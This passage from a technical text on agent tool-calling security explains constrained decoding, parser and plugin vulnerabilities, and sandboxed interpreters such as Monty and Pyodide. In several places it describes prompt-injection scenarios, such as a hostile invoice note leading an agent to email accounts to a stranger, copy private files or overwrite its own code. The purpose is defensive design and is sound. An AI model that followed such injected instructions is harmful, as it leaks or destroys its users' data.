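LangChain's early components had to search the model's prose for markers of code or tool requests. Model providers began to offer an interface for this in June 2023, when OpenAI's *Function calling and other API updates* announced versions of GPT-4 and GPT-3.5 Turbo trained to recognise when a request called for a function and to reply with JSON that matched the function's description. The announcement's first example was `send_email(to, body)`.

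Training made well-formed calls likely but didn't guarantee them. Later in 2023 OpenAI added a "JSON mode", which made valid JSON more likely but didn't enforce a particular schema. Willison (2024), in *OpenAI*, recalled that both methods usually worked but could still produce output that didn't match the schema or wasn't JSON at all. Developers often handled these failures by sending the request again. People who ran open-weight models themselves already had a better option, because tools such as jsonformer could control which token came next.

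OpenAI adopted that approach in August 2024, when it introduced strict schemas. *Introducing Structured Outputs in the API* (2024) reports that in OpenAI's own test of complicated schemas, the June 2023 version of GPT-4 matched them less than 40% of the time. Further training brought a newer model, GPT-4o, to 93%, and controlling its choice of tokens brought it to 100%.

### Constrained decoding

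The last seven points come from a technique called constrained decoding. A model writes one token at a time. At each step it assigns a probability to every token in its vocabulary, and the software running the model picks one. With constrained decoding, the software first works out which tokens could continue the text without breaking the schema. It sets the probability of every other token to zero and scales up the remaining probabilities so they add up to one again.

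In symbols, let *p*(*t*) be the model's probability for token *t*, and let *A* be the set of tokens the schema allows at that point. The new probability is

*p*′(*t*) = *p*(*t*) / *Z* if *t* is in *A*, and 0 otherwise,

where *Z* is the total probability the model gave to the tokens in *A*.

The allowed set changes as the text grows. At the start of the arguments for `send_email`, the model might otherwise write "Sure, I'll send that", but the schema requires an opening curly bracket, so the software rules out "Sure". The name of a field comes next. Once the model has opened the quotation marks around the recipient's address, almost any text is allowed, because the schema only requires `to` to be a string.

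A developer can narrow that with an enumeration, written `enum` in a schema, which lists the permitted values. Suppose `to` may be only `finance@example.com` or `billing@example.com`, and a hostile note on an invoice has told the model to write to a stranger. The probabilities for the start of the address might then be as follows (the numbers are invented, and each name counts as one token):

| Next token | Any string allowed | Two addresses allowed |
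|---|---|---|
| finance | 0.20 | 0.80 |
| billing | 0.05 | 0.20 |
| stranger | 0.75 | 0 |

The two permitted tokens had a total probability of 0.25, so each becomes four times as likely. If the schema requires only a plain string, it allows the stranger's address.

OpenAI converts each schema into the same general kind of grammar as the four rules for arithmetic in the previous section. Some other systems use finite-state machines, which are simpler but can't keep track of brackets nested to any depth. When OpenAI launched the feature, preparing the grammar added up to ten seconds to the first request with a typical schema, and could add a minute for a complex one. Later requests with the same schema reused the stored grammar. A developer who put a new list of permitted customers in the schema for every request would therefore have faced the delay each time.

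*Constrained Decoding for Diffusion Language Models via Efficient Inference over Finite Automata* (2026) gives examples of mistakes that constrained decoding prevents. An unconstrained model answered in prose when it should have called a tool, miscapitalized an argument's name, and invented a function that wasn't on the list. The same model got those examples right with the constraint.

### Effects on answer quality

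Developers have worried that forcing a model to follow a format makes its answers worse. Tam and colleagues reported in 2024 that models reasoned less well inside a JSON schema than in free text, and several later studies also found drops in performance. *Constrained Decoding* (Nguyen, Silva and colleagues, 2026) argues that most of these studies compared different prompts and output formats but attributed the difference in results to the constraint.

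Their case includes a short proof. Suppose the model has finished reasoning and is about to write its answer, and the schema allows the correct one. At every step, the constraint divides the probability of the correct token by *Z*, which is at most one, so the probability of the whole correct answer rises or stays the same. In the email example, if the finance team is the right recipient, the chance of choosing it rises from 0.20 to 0.80.

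They also tested eleven open models with 1.7 to 32 billion parameters (the numbers a model learns in training). When the prompt and the expected format were the same, constrained decoding did at least as well as unconstrained decoding. In one task, joining the last letters of several names, the models reasoned in free text and a second model then extracted the answer. Constraining only the extraction raised accuracy by about three to six percentage points for each of the six models in that comparison.

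Where the model reasons matters more. With the constraint applied in both cases, four of the six models scored higher when they reasoned freely and formatted the answer afterwards than when they reasoned in a JSON field. Qwen3.5-4B scored 86.9% with free reasoning and 71.6% with reasoning in the field. Qwen3-8B did better reasoning in the field, scoring 78.4% compared with 72.4%.

The proof depends on the schema allowing the correct answer. For an agent, the correct answer is sometimes to call no tool, and a schema can make that harder. Lee (2026), in *Repair, Not Improvement*, gave three small Qwen models requests in English and Korean, with ten possible tools for each request. Half the requests needed one of the tools and half needed none. The constrained models had to answer with a tool's name or the word "None".

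The constraint improved the choice of tool in every case, compared with letting the models explain themselves. But in four of the six combinations of model and language, it reduced the share of correct "None" answers, by as much as 29.5 percentage points. Some of that drop came from limiting the answer to one line. To isolate the effect of the list, Lee also tested unconstrained one-line answers. For the smallest model in English, adding the list raised correct tool choices from 16.5% to 43.0% and cut correct "None" answers from 59.0% to 35.5%.

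This doesn't contradict the proof, which concerns one exact wording of the answer and a model that picks tokens at random according to their probabilities. Lee's models always took the most likely token, and the scoring accepted longer replies that contained "None". When a model would otherwise have declined in a full sentence, its most likely opening may have been forbidden, and the most likely permitted opening may have been the name of a tool.

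Lee tested only models with up to four billion parameters, so large commercial models may lose much less. The result is still a good reason to include requests that need no tool when testing an agent. Lee points out that a router forced to choose a tool every time will call a weather service to answer a legal question.

### What the schema leaves open

With constrained decoding, a completed call names a function on the developer's list, supplies the required arguments in the declared types, and takes any enumerated values from the permitted set. OpenAI's version had three exceptions at launch: the model could refuse a request, the output could reach its length limit before the call was complete, and parallel calls might not match their schemas.

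A framework can get the same guarantee by checking the reply after it arrives, as the four lines of Python do. Constrained decoding then mainly reduces the number of failed attempts. For security, the application's own check is more reliable, because constrained decoding usually runs on the provider's machines and the application can't confirm that it worked.

The guarantee covers only some of what the owner of the invoice agent needs to know:

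| Question about the call | Does the schema settle it? |
|---|---|
| Is `send_email` on the list of tools? | Yes |
| Are `to` and `body` both present, and both text? | Yes |
| Should this recipient see the total? | No, unless `to` is limited to suitable addresses |
| Is 2,000 the right total? | No |
| Should the agent send an email at all? | No |
| Is it safe for `send_email` to use this text? | No |

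Several experiments show that a schema leaves room for mistakes. *Inference for Reasoning Models* (2026) tested models on BFCL, the benchmark that Patel and colleagues used. The Llama and Mistral models already produced valid calls every time, and adding a schema changed their accuracy by 0.0 percentage points. *Brief Is Better* (2026) restricted two small models to real function names. Without reasoning first, they chose the wrong function 24.5% and 9.5% of the time. After a few words of reasoning, they always chose the right function, but more than a third of their calls still failed because of the arguments.

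A valid format can also hide a failure. An application detects broken JSON at once but accepts a well-formed call with the wrong amount. *The Constraint Tax* (2026) calls this outcome "wrong answer, valid schema" and describes it as a particular danger with models under three billion parameters.

The last question in the table matters most for code execution. A schema can require an argument to be text, but the function may then run that text as code. The LoLLMs calculator did this with arithmetic expressions, and Semantic Kernel's hotel search did it with city names. OpenAI's 2023 announcement included an example tool, `sql_query(query)`, whose only argument is a string of SQL, so any SQL statement satisfies the schema, including one that deletes the invoices.

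OpenAI's 2024 post has a much safer design for a similar job. The schema for its `query` tool enumerates one table name, seven column names and six comparison operators. A model can request orders delivered after a certain date, but it cannot express a deletion. The schema is in effect a restricted language written in JSON. It stays restricted only if the function carries out the comparison itself. Pasting the values into SQL or Python would again let model output run as code, because the comparison value can be any string.

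### vLLM's tool-call parser

The framework has to parse a call before it can validate it, and a flaw in vLLM, a program that runs models, shows that parsing can be dangerous too. Models write tool calls in different formats. Qwen3-Coder, a programming model, uses one similar to XML, in which every argument arrives as text, so the parser has to convert "90" to a number if the tool's schema requires one.

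The GitHub user ranpox (2025) submitted a parser for this format on 22 July 2025. It converted common types with ordinary functions and passed arguments of any other declared type to Python's `eval`, which turns "[1, 2]" into a list but also runs any other Python expression. This was incidental evaluation, since nobody intended the argument to be a program.

An automated code reviewer flagged the call to `eval` as critical the same day, because users could influence the model's output, and recommended removing it. A maintainer merged the code that day anyway, "to unblock model usage". Unlike in the case of the missing warnings in Python's manual, the right advice was available here, but the maintainer seems to have put supporting a new model quickly first.

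GitLab's *CVE-2025-9141* (2025) dates the public disclosure to 21 August. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2014* (2026), an entry in a database of open-source vulnerabilities, the flaw affected servers with tool calling turned on and this parser selected. An attacker needed an account and had to get the model to pass code as an argument. The entry rates the severity 8.8 out of 10 and lists version 0.10.1.1 as the fix.

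The code ran on the model's server before the application received the call, so validation in the application would have come too late, however strict the schema.

After the fix, vLLM uses `ast.literal_eval` in place of `eval`. It accepts values written out in full, such as numbers, strings and lists, and rejects anything that would have to be run, such as a function call. If `literal_eval` can't read the text, the parser keeps the argument as a string. The model can still supply lists, so the fix removed almost no functionality.

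The same source code shows why a tool shouldn't rely on the declared types. If a schema requires a whole number and the model outputs "ninety", the parser logs a warning and passes on the string. That is a reasonable way to handle a model's mistakes, but the application may receive a value its schema forbids.

### Semantic Kernel's download helper

A list of callable functions protects an application only if the right functions are on it. Microsoft's Semantic Kernel has a plugin that runs model-written Python in an isolated cloud session with its own files. The helper functions that copy files between that session and the host, the machine running the agent, have to run on the host, outside the isolation.

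In the version for .NET, Microsoft's software platform, a developer makes a function available to the model by placing a label called an attribute above it. Microsoft found that the download helper had this attribute by mistake, so the framework presented it to the model as a tool, along with its parameters. One parameter was the path where the host would save the file, and the helper didn't check that path.

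An attacker who could steer the model could make the agent write a file almost anywhere the application had permission to write, and from there get code running on the host. Every call would have been valid under the schema, because a path is just a string. The isolation also worked as intended, since the file left through a function that the host provided. The upload helper, in both the .NET and Python versions, accepted any local path, so injected text could make the agent copy private files into the session.

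This flaw is CVE-2026-25592. Version 1.71.0 fixed it mainly by removing the attribute, so the model can no longer call the download helper. Developers can still call it from their own code, but it now checks the path against a list of permitted folders. It resolves the path to its full form first, because a path can contain shortcuts that lead out of the folder it appears to be in. Microsoft added similar protection for uploads, but developers have to turn it on.

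NIST's *CVE-2026-25592 Detail* (2026) suggested that anyone who couldn't upgrade add a filter that runs before each call to either helper and accepts only approved paths. This is weaker than removing the tool, because the model can still call a function it never needed.

A single misplaced attribute is easy to miss in code review. An automated test could catch it by comparing the tools the framework advertises with a list the developer wrote by hand. The test would fail whenever a new tool appeared, and somebody would have to decide whether the model should have it.

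### Designing tools that limit a bad call

Both flaws support Microsoft's advice to distrust any tool input the model can influence. The most effective response is usually to give the model fewer and narrower parameters. To remind customers about overdue invoices, the agent doesn't need a general email tool:

```python
def send_reminder(invoice_id):
    invoice = find_invoice(invoice_id)   # error if there is none
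    if invoice.days_overdue <= 90 or invoice.reminder_sent:
        raise ValueError("no reminder due")
    email(invoice.customer_address, REMINDER_TEXT)
    invoice.reminder_sent = True
```

The model chooses only an invoice. The developer's code looks up the address, supplies the wording and prevents a second reminder. A hostile note could still make the agent remind a customer who paid last week, which is embarrassing but far less serious than sending the accounts to a stranger. This design requires the developer to write a separate function for each kind of email.

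Enumerated values suit choices that rarely change, such as departments or report types. They work less well for customers, whose list grows every day, so the function can check the customer against the database instead. The agent should also be able to call no tool, because Lee's small models often picked one when none was suitable.

The function should check its arguments even when the schema already covers them, because vLLM's parser can pass on the wrong type and another part of the program may call the function without any schema. The function can also apply rules that a schema can't express, such as the check on `days_overdue`, which depends on the current state of the accounts. A function that emails the overdue total could calculate it from the database, so that the model couldn't get it wrong.

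Some calls are consequential enough to need a person's approval. When OpenAI launched function calling in 2023, it recommended getting this approval before actions such as sending an email, posting online or making a purchase. It also warned of prompt injection through a tool's output. The approval screen should show the recipient and text from the call itself, because a summary written by the model could be misleading.

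Approval works only if people read what they approve. Someone who has to confirm 40 reminders one at a time will probably start clicking without looking. The developer could instead show all 40 in one table, with their amounts and dates, and ask for approval once.

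## Interpreters that start with no access

A function like `send_reminder` limits the damage from a bad call, but the developer has to foresee each job and write a function for it. A model that writes programs can combine such functions in ways the developer never planned. A capability-limited interpreter allows this without granting all the access that `exec` does, because its programs can reach things outside the interpreter only through functions the application provides.

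### Object capabilities

When ordinary Python runs `open("accounts.txt")`, the string only names a file. The right to read that file comes from the process as a whole. Security researchers call this ambient authority, because code has it without anyone granting it for the specific task.

In the object-capability model, a program has no ambient authority. It can use a resource only if it holds a reference to that resource, called a capability, and it needs no other permission. If the application opens `accounts.txt` and passes the open file to a program, the program can read that file and no other. Knowing that `salaries.txt` exists doesn't help an attacker, because the program can't turn a filename into a capability.

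The model works only if a program has no way to get a reference except by receiving it from the host, creating a new object, or getting it from an object it already holds. Objects also have to hide their inner workings. Otherwise a program holding a harmless email function could look inside it and take the mail server's login.

A developer can limit what code can do by giving it a function instead of the resource behind it. Code that holds `email_finance_total` can send the finance team a number, although the function uses a login that could send anything to anyone. Pydantic's *Security Model*, part of the documentation for the company's Monty interpreter, gives a similar example in which the host lets a program read a bank account's owner and balance and call `withdraw`. The program can't call `close`, because the developer didn't list it. If a permitted method returns another object, the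 call fails unless the developer has chosen rules for that object too, so a program can't use a harmless object to reach a powerful one.

Capabilities also help with confused deputies, which are programs that an outsider tricks into misusing their own access. The outsider usually supplies a name, such as a file path, for something that only the program has the right to use. If the outsider must supply a capability instead, they can supply only one they already hold. A host function that reads any path it is given undoes this protection, because it lets the interpreted code read every file the application can open. Pydantic warns that no interpreter can prevent that.

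A developer can limit what programs reach by removing the dangerous parts of a full interpreter, or by starting with an interpreter that can't reach anything and adding functions. Pydantic compares these approaches to a firewall that blocks ports known to be bad and one that blocks everything except approved traffic. Starting with no access is safer when the developer overlooks a function, because that function is missing from the interpreter rather than left available for a program to escape through.

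### Python's abandoned sandboxes

Python's developers first tried removing the dangerous features. The standard library once included `rexec` (restricted execution), which ran code with a reduced set of built-in functions. It replaced the functions for opening files and importing modules with versions that checked each request.

Python 2.2 changed how classes worked, and the new classes gave programs new ways to escape `rexec`. In 2003 the developers disabled `rexec` in Python 2.3. They explained in the release notes that nobody had the time or interest to fix it, and warned users not to go back to an older version, because `rexec` had known holes there too. They removed the module in Python 3.

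Victor Stinner, a Python core developer, made another attempt with pysandbox, which ran untrusted code in the standard interpreter, CPython, and hid the objects and attributes that led out of the sandbox. In November 2013, after three years of work, Stinner announced that the project was broken by design. Python lets programs inspect their own objects in such detail that there were too many routes out. Closing them had also made the sandbox almost useless, since programs could no longer even delete an entry from a dictionary. Stinner concluded that developers should run the whole Python process in a sandbox rather than try to build one within the interpreter.

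Both projects ran into the same links between values, types and the rest of the interpreter that later defeated Semantic Kernel's search filter. People still write such sandboxes for other purposes. Hermetic is one example, and its *Threat Model* warns that it is not a security boundary. The document recommends Hermetic for software tests, and for plugins or models that behave badly without malice, such as a library that fetches a file from the internet without being asked.

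### LocalPythonExecutor

Hugging Face's smolagents, a framework built around code actions, falls between the two designs. Its LocalPythonExecutor parses the model's program into a syntax tree and carries out each node itself, much as the short `value` function did for arithmetic, instead of passing the program to `exec`.

*Autonomous AI Agents* (Williams, 2025), an article for the security company NCC Group, describes the restrictions. The executor rejects any kind of node it doesn't recognise and stops programs that carry out too many operations. By default it allows only 11 modules, including `math`, `re` and `datetime`, and it tries to stop programs from reaching forbidden modules through permitted ones. The current version also stops programs after 30 seconds unless the developer changes the limit.

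This is far stricter than PALChain's list of four banned names. But the executor is a Python program, and it handles ordinary Python objects in the application's process. If the model's program reads an attribute of a list, the executor looks it up on a real list, which has the usual links to the rest of Python. So although the executor restricts the language, it still has to block every dangerous route through the objects.

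Researchers found gaps in the executor in 2025. According to NVD's *CVE-2025-5120 Detail*, version 1.14.0 didn't sufficiently restrict the modules and functions on its permitted list, so an attacker could use them to run arbitrary code on the host. Hugging Face fixed this in version 1.17.0. The next flaw, CVE-2025-9959, came from incomplete checks on Python's special attributes, whose names begin and end with two underscores. According to GCVE's *Sandbox escape in smolagents Local Python execution environment via dunder attributes* (2025), its severity is 7.6 out of 10, and an attacker would need prompt injection to get the agent to write the hostile code. Version 1.21.0 fixed it. CISA listed no known exploitation when the record appeared.

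Developers can also weaken the restrictions themselves, through a smolagents setting that adds modules to the permitted list. Williams found this setting used in an example from Hugging Face's own course on agents, which more than 100,000 people had signed up for. The example added the data libraries pandas and NumPy, among others, without a warning, although these libraries can read and write files. An attacker who controls part of the prompt might therefore get the agent to overwrite its own source code, which would later run with full rights. In Williams' tests, agents with these libraries read and wrote files on request, though not every time.

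A developer who adds pandas probably means to allow statistics, but doing so also gives the agent access to every file the application can open. Williams recommends keeping the default list and writing a specific tool for anything else the agent needs.

Hugging Face's *Python code executors* now describes LocalPythonExecutor as "not a security sandbox" and directs developers to remote executors for untrusted code. This is fairer than NVD's description of the executor as a core security boundary. The restrictions still catch many of a model's accidental errors, but an application that reads strangers' emails or invoices needs stronger protection.

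### Running the invoice script in Monty

Pydantic released Monty, an interpreter for part of the Python language, in February 2026. It is written in Rust and shares no code with CPython's core. It has no instruction that opens a file, connects to a network or starts a program.

To run the two-line invoice script, an application first supplies the two functions that the script calls:

```python
from collections import namedtuple
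from pydantic_monty import Monty

Invoice = namedtuple("Invoice", "amount days_overdue")

def list_invoices():
    return [Invoice(1200, 120), Invoice(800, 95), Invoice(500, 30)]

def send_email(to, body):
    ...                          # the application's own mail code

tools = {"list_invoices": list_invoices, "send_email": send_email}
limits = {"max_memory": 10_000_000, "max_feed_duration_secs": 1.0}

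with Monty(request_timeout=10) as pool:
    with pool.checkout(limits=limits) as session:
        session.feed_run(script, external_lookup=tools)
```

Here `script` is the text from the model. In a real application, `list_invoices` would query the accounting database instead of returning fixed values.

Monty first parses the script with the parser from Ruff, a tool that checks Python code for errors. If the script contains syntax that Monty doesn't support, Monty stops with an error before running anything.

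The developer can also turn on a type check, which compares the script with declarations of the host functions. The declaration for the email tool would be:

```python
def send_email(to: str, body: str) -> None: ...
```

A script that passed the number 2000 as the body would fail this check, because the declaration requires text. If the developer also declares the fields of an invoice, the check can catch a wrongly guessed field name such as `i.age`. The application can then return the error to the model and ask for a corrected script.

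Next, Monty compiles the script to bytecode, a list of simple instructions, and starts to run it. The script calls `list_invoices`, which it doesn't define, so Monty pauses and passes the function's name and arguments to the application. The application looks up the name in `tools`, runs its own function with its own database login and returns the three invoices. Monty resumes, keeps the two that are more than 90 days overdue and adds their amounts to get 2,000. It pauses again at `send_email` and passes the recipient and text to the application, which sends the email.

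The database login never enters the interpreter. Monty runs in a separate worker process. On most systems, the application starts that process with an empty environment, so it doesn't inherit passwords or keys stored in environment variables. If a customer's note had led the model to add `open("accounts.txt")`, the call would fail because the developer has given the script no files. A call to a function missing from `tools` would also fail because its name would be undefined.

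Monty has its own `eval` and `exec`. As in CPython, the code they run has the same access as the program that calls them, but here that program has access only to `list_invoices` and `send_email`.

### Pauses, files and limits

The application can delay its answer to a host call. Pydantic's *Getting Started with Python* shows how to inspect the called function's name and arguments at each pause and save the paused program. For the invoice agent, the developer could save the script at `send_email`, show the bookkeeper the actual recipient and text, and resume after approval, even on another machine. Pydantic reports that a saved program takes a few kilobytes. The application has to protect saved programs against tampering, because Monty doesn't check where they came from.

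Some tasks need files, so Monty lets a developer share a folder with the program, read-only if necessary. Monty opens the folder once and performs every later operation relative to it, so the open folder acts as a capability. The program cannot name a location outside the folder, although a bug in Monty's file code could still let it reach files there. Semantic Kernel's repaired download helper instead checks each path against a list, so its safety depends on making that comparison correctly every time.

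By default, programs can read the clock and get random numbers. Pydantic calls the clock a weak capability because a program can use it to time operations, and those timings can sometimes reveal information. A developer can freeze the clock at a chosen time.

Monty can also limit memory, which Starlark's Go interpreter can't do from inside. Monty rejects some huge requests in advance, such as one for a string of a trillion characters. The time limit in the invoice example allows one second of execution, not counting time spent waiting for a host function, so a slow mail server won't stop the script. A separate limit on the number of pauses stops a program that makes endless quick calls to the host.

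Monty checks the time limit only at certain points while running a program, so a bug in the interpreter could make it hang between checks. The `request_timeout` setting covers this by killing the worker process, but it is off by default when Monty runs locally. Pydantic also advises developers to discard a session that exceeds its time or memory limit, because its data may no longer be reliable, but Monty doesn't do this automatically.

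### What Monty leaves out

Monty supported very little of Python at launch and has since grown quickly. Pydantic's *Limitations* gives the current state:

| Feature | At launch | Late 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Functions, loops and comprehensions | Yes | Yes |
| Classes | No | Simple ones |
| `match` and `with` statements | No | Yes |
| `json`, `re` and `datetime` modules | No | Yes |
| Standard library modules in all | 4 | About 30, most only in part |
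| Third-party packages | No | No |

It still rejects `del` and `yield`, and a program can't define its own exceptions. Pydantic hasn't yet written some of the missing modules, such as `enum` and `string`. It leaves out others on purpose, including `socket` and `subprocess`, because they would breach the sandbox.

The lack of third-party packages matters most for data questions. The data-frame agent's single line of pandas can't run in Monty, so the developer would have to provide a host function or pass in the table as a wrapped object. The wrapper exposes only the methods the developer lists. Listing them one by one is tedious, but a shortcut allows every public method a class defines. With a pandas table, that would include methods that write files, the same problem Williams found in the smolagents course.

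### Attempts to break out

Monty's design depends on the interpreter having no serious bugs. In its launch article, Pydantic wrote that several people seemed to have tried and failed to break out, but that "real hardness comes with time and stress". In April 2026, Pydantic offered $5,000 to anyone who could read a secret on a server running Monty. The server received almost 1.5 million requests from about 650 internet addresses, and Owen Kwan of the security company Veria Labs read the secret in less than 48 hours.

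*Hack Monty* (Hewitt, 2026), Pydantic's account of the contest, traces the escape to a use-after-free, a memory error in which a program keeps using memory after releasing it, by which time an attacker may have put something else there. Rust normally prevents such errors, but programmers can bypass some of its checks in sections marked `unsafe`. One of Monty's `unsafe` sections relied on an assumption about which objects were still in memory, and a bug in the code that clears away unused objects made that assumption false. Pydantic fixed the bug in version 0.0.16. It also paid $300 to Stanislav Fort of the security company AISLE for finding a weakness in the contest's virtual file system, though the weakness wasn't enough to reveal the secret.

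Kwan's escape worked by corrupting the interpreter's memory, which lets an attacker make the process do things that no Monty program could express. It didn't depend on a dangerous function that Pydantic had forgotten to remove. Starting with no access removes the many routes that defeated pysandbox, but it doesn't protect against a memory error in the interpreter.

At the time, Monty ran inside the application's process, so it started very quickly. Prefect, whose FastMCP framework uses Monty by default, described the drawback in *Hack Monty 2* (Colvin, 2026), the announcement of the next contest: "Embedded also means a sandbox escape is a host compromise."

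Nobody escaped in that second round, which began on 30 May with a prize of $10,000. Pydantic's *Hack Monty Round 3 & Round 2 results* reports only crashes, problems with limits and differences from CPython. The company raised the prize to $20,000 for a third round in August and now runs a permanent bounty programme. This result is encouraging, but it can't show that no escape exists. Someone who finds an escape from a widely used interpreter may be able to sell it for more than the prize.

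Pydantic has since moved the interpreter into a separate worker process. A crash now ends only the worker, and code that escapes no longer ends up in the application's memory. Escaped code would still run on the same machine, normally with the same user's file permissions, because Monty adds no operating-system protections. A compromised worker could also see later sessions. By default the application replaces each worker after 1,000 sessions, and Pydantic recommends replacing it after every session if users don't trust one another. For stronger protection, a developer can run the workers on another machine, so that escaped code doesn't reach the machine with the accounting login.

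Apart from the contests, some outside evidence comes from *pydantic-monty investigation* (Willison, 2026). Willison had Claude Code examine the latest release in May, and the limits on time, memory and recursion appeared to work as advertised. This check of the documentation is useful but much less thorough than a security audit.

Monty has also changed very fast. Pydantic's *monty 0.0.21* was still labeled "not ready for prime time", while the package page from Pydantic (2026) marks version 1.7.0, released on 24 November, as stable. The interpreter may well be reliable enough to be called stable, but the version people now install has not been in use long enough for a thorough test of its security, and much of its code is newer than the first contest.

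### Can models work around the gaps?

Critics object that Monty is incomplete as well as new. In *Monty*, dmpetrov's online discussion thread about the launch, one commenter called it absurd to use a "half baked" interpreter that would always lag behind CPython. The commenter recommended sandboxing CPython with operating system features, which is essentially what Stinner concluded in 2013.

In *Running Pydantic's Monty Rust sandboxed Python subset in WebAssembly*, Willison didn't see the missing features as a problem. A model that tries to define a class gets an error message and can rewrite the program without the class. This would infuriate a human programmer, but models are good at correcting code from error messages, and agent scripts are usually short.

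This is a good reply when the error comes before the script has done anything. Monty rejects unsupported syntax at the start, and the type check catches many missing functions. Other errors appear only while the script is running. Suppose a script sends 40 reminders in a loop and fails on the 21st. If the model corrects the script and the application runs it from the beginning, 20 customers get a second reminder. Pydantic warns developers to retry only when it is safe to repeat what the host functions have already done. The `send_reminder` function from the previous section is safe to repeat because it doesn't remind the same customer twice.

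Retries also reduce the savings from code actions. The invoice script saves only one model call, so a single failed attempt removes the advantage.

Differences that cause no error are harder to deal with. In Python, a class can define a `__bool__` method to decide whether its objects count as true or false. Monty ignores this method, so such objects always count as true. If a model wrote a `Balance` class that counted as false at zero, the code under `if balance:` would run even for customers who owe nothing, and no error message would prompt the model to rewrite the script. Pydantic documents this difference and many others, but a developer would have to put the relevant ones in the prompt or test for them.

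Pydantic's results suggest that such problems don't outweigh the benefits of code. *Agent Sandboxes*, the company's page for its hosted version of Monty, reports an October 2026 benchmark of eight models on long tasks. Seven succeeded more often when they wrote code for Monty than when they used structured tool calls, and the eighth succeeded every time with both. Claude Haiku 5.5's success rate rose from 64% with tool calls to 94% with code. The benchmark didn't include full Python, so it doesn't show how much the missing features lower success rates, and Pydantic sells the product it tested.

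Willison's reply answers the complaint that Monty is incomplete, but a model's skill at rewriting code doesn't make a new interpreter secure. CPython's age doesn't make it secure either, since its developers never built it to contain hostile code and gave up on `rexec`. An application with valuable data can run Monty's workers inside an operating-system sandbox, so an attacker has to break through both. Adding the sandbox gives up some of Monty's simplicity and may be unnecessary for an internal tool that reads only trusted data.

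Monty suits agents, like the invoice agent, that mostly call functions and do some calculation between calls. Agents that install packages, run build tools or work with a real file system need a complete computer, and Pydantic recommends a container or virtual machine for those.

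## WebAssembly sandboxes, containers and virtual machines

An agent that needs pandas or a real file system usually has to run the standard Python interpreter. Nobody has managed to confine that interpreter from within, so the alternative is to isolate it from the outside. WebAssembly can isolate a single program inside a process, a container isolates a group of processes that share an operating system, and a virtual machine isolates an entire operating system.

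WebAssembly sandboxes, containers and virtual machines all leave Python's dangerous functions in place and try to make them harmless. How well they work depends on the software that enforces the barrier and on what the developer lets through it. In 2025 and 2026, researchers broke out of several products that ran Python in WebAssembly, mostly because of the software around the WebAssembly module.

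### How WebAssembly confines a program

WebAssembly is a portable instruction format that browser makers designed so that web pages could run programs written in languages such as C. A compiler turns the source code into a file called a module. A runtime on the user's machine then translates the module into instructions for that machine's processor. Browsers include a runtime, and Wasmtime is a popular one for use outside browsers.

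A module keeps most of its data in linear memory, a block of bytes numbered from zero. A pointer in the C source becomes a position in this block, so the module can't express an address anywhere else in the process. The runtime also has to reject positions beyond the end. If the memory has *n* bytes, a module may read *k* bytes from position *a* only if

*a* + *k* ≤ *n*.

In a memory of 65,536 bytes, for example, a module can read four bytes at position 65,532. The same read at 65,533 causes a trap, which stops the program immediately. The WebAssembly project's *Security* page adds that the runtime must calculate positions exactly, because a sum that wrapped round to a small number would pass the bounds check.

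Wasmtime normally omits the explicit bounds check and relies on the processor to catch out-of-bounds reads. It arranges the process's memory so that a position past the end of the module's memory falls on unreadable addresses. According to Wasmtime's *Security* page, it also reserves two gigabytes of inaccessible addresses before the module's memory. No module should ever reach them, but they give some protection if Wasmtime's compiler mistakes a large position for a negative one.

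WebAssembly checks that a program stays within its module's block of memory, but it doesn't check the bounds of each object in that block. A C program that writes past the end of an array can therefore overwrite whatever comes next in the block. A hostile script could use a bug like this to corrupt a Python interpreter running in WebAssembly, but the corruption would stay inside the module's memory.

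WebAssembly also limits where a program can jump. In ordinary machine code, an attacker may redirect a program by overwriting a stored return address. The WebAssembly runtime keeps return addresses outside linear memory. A module must declare its functions when it loads and calls them by number, and a branch can lead only to a valid point in the same function. When a program chooses a function while running, the runtime checks that the function has the expected types. An attacker can sometimes redirect such a call to another function with the same types, but only to one the module could already access.

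WebAssembly has no instruction for a system call, which an ordinary program uses to have the operating system open a file or a network connection. A module can affect the outside world only through its imports, which are functions the host supplies. This applies the object-capability model to a compiled program instead of to the values in a scripting language.

### Granting files and network access through WASI

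A module with no imports can't read the clock. The WebAssembly System Interface (WASI) is a standard set of functions that a module can import to use files, clocks, random numbers and networking. The module can use only the resources that the host grants it.

Suppose the invoice application saves the invoices to a folder for a script to read. In the oldest version of WASI still in use, the host opens the folder before the module starts and passes the module a handle to it. The module can open files inside that folder, but it can't request a handle to anything else. Wasmtime lets the developer make any folder read-only, and doing so here would prevent the script from changing or deleting the invoices.

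Newer versions of WASI divide these powers into separate imports. The program's file lists them, so a developer can check whether the program could open a network connection. Before WASI 0.3, released in June 2026, programs passed a network handle into each operation. Now the host grants network access to the program as a whole. This is easier to use but slightly less precise, because a program can no longer deny network access to one of its own libraries.

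WASI's *Security* page calls this stronger than typical process isolation because the limits apply regardless of what the host process is allowed to do. That is true only if the runtime enforces the limits correctly. RustSec's *Filesystem sandbox escape when paths or symlinks contain trailing slashes* (2026) describes a flaw in how Wasmtime handled file paths that let code get around the folder limit. The advisory rates the flaw's severity 8.8 out of 10 and lists fixes for four release series.

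Other runtimes don't attempt the same protection. Node.js, which runs JavaScript outside browsers, also has a WASI module, but its documentation page *WebAssembly System Interface (WASI)* advises developers not to rely on the module for untrusted code. The same program may therefore be confined to one folder under Wasmtime but have wider access under Node.js.

### Python and its packages in WebAssembly

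The CPython interpreter is written in C, so a compiler can turn it into a WebAssembly module. Pyodide is a version of CPython built this way with Emscripten, a set of tools for compiling C to WebAssembly. The model's script stays ordinary text, which the interpreter inside the module reads and runs. Cloudflare uses Pyodide to run its customers' Python programs and reports that Pyodide passes most of CPython's tests.

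Pyodide runs far more existing code than Monty does. Pyodide's *FAQ* gives these rules for packages:

| Kind of package | Does it work? |
|---|---|
| Contains only Python code | Usually |
| Has parts written in C or C++ | Usually, after somebody compiles them for WebAssembly |
| Needs threads or several processes | No |
| Starts other programs | No |
| Opens raw network connections | No, though `requests` and `httpx` have substitutes |

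Pyodide provides working versions of NumPy and pandas, including their compiled parts. The data-frame agent's line of pandas code can therefore run in a WebAssembly sandbox without the developer having to write a wrapper.

Until June 2026, Pyodide's maintainers had to build and host more than 300 packages themselves. Version 314.0 lets package developers publish their own WebAssembly builds on PyPI, Python's public package index (Willison, 2026, *Publishing WASM wheels to PyPI for use with Pyodide*). This should gradually make more packages available. Thread support will probably take longer. According to a Python design proposal, threads would require websites to send special security headers, and combining them with libraries loaded while the program runs is still experimental.

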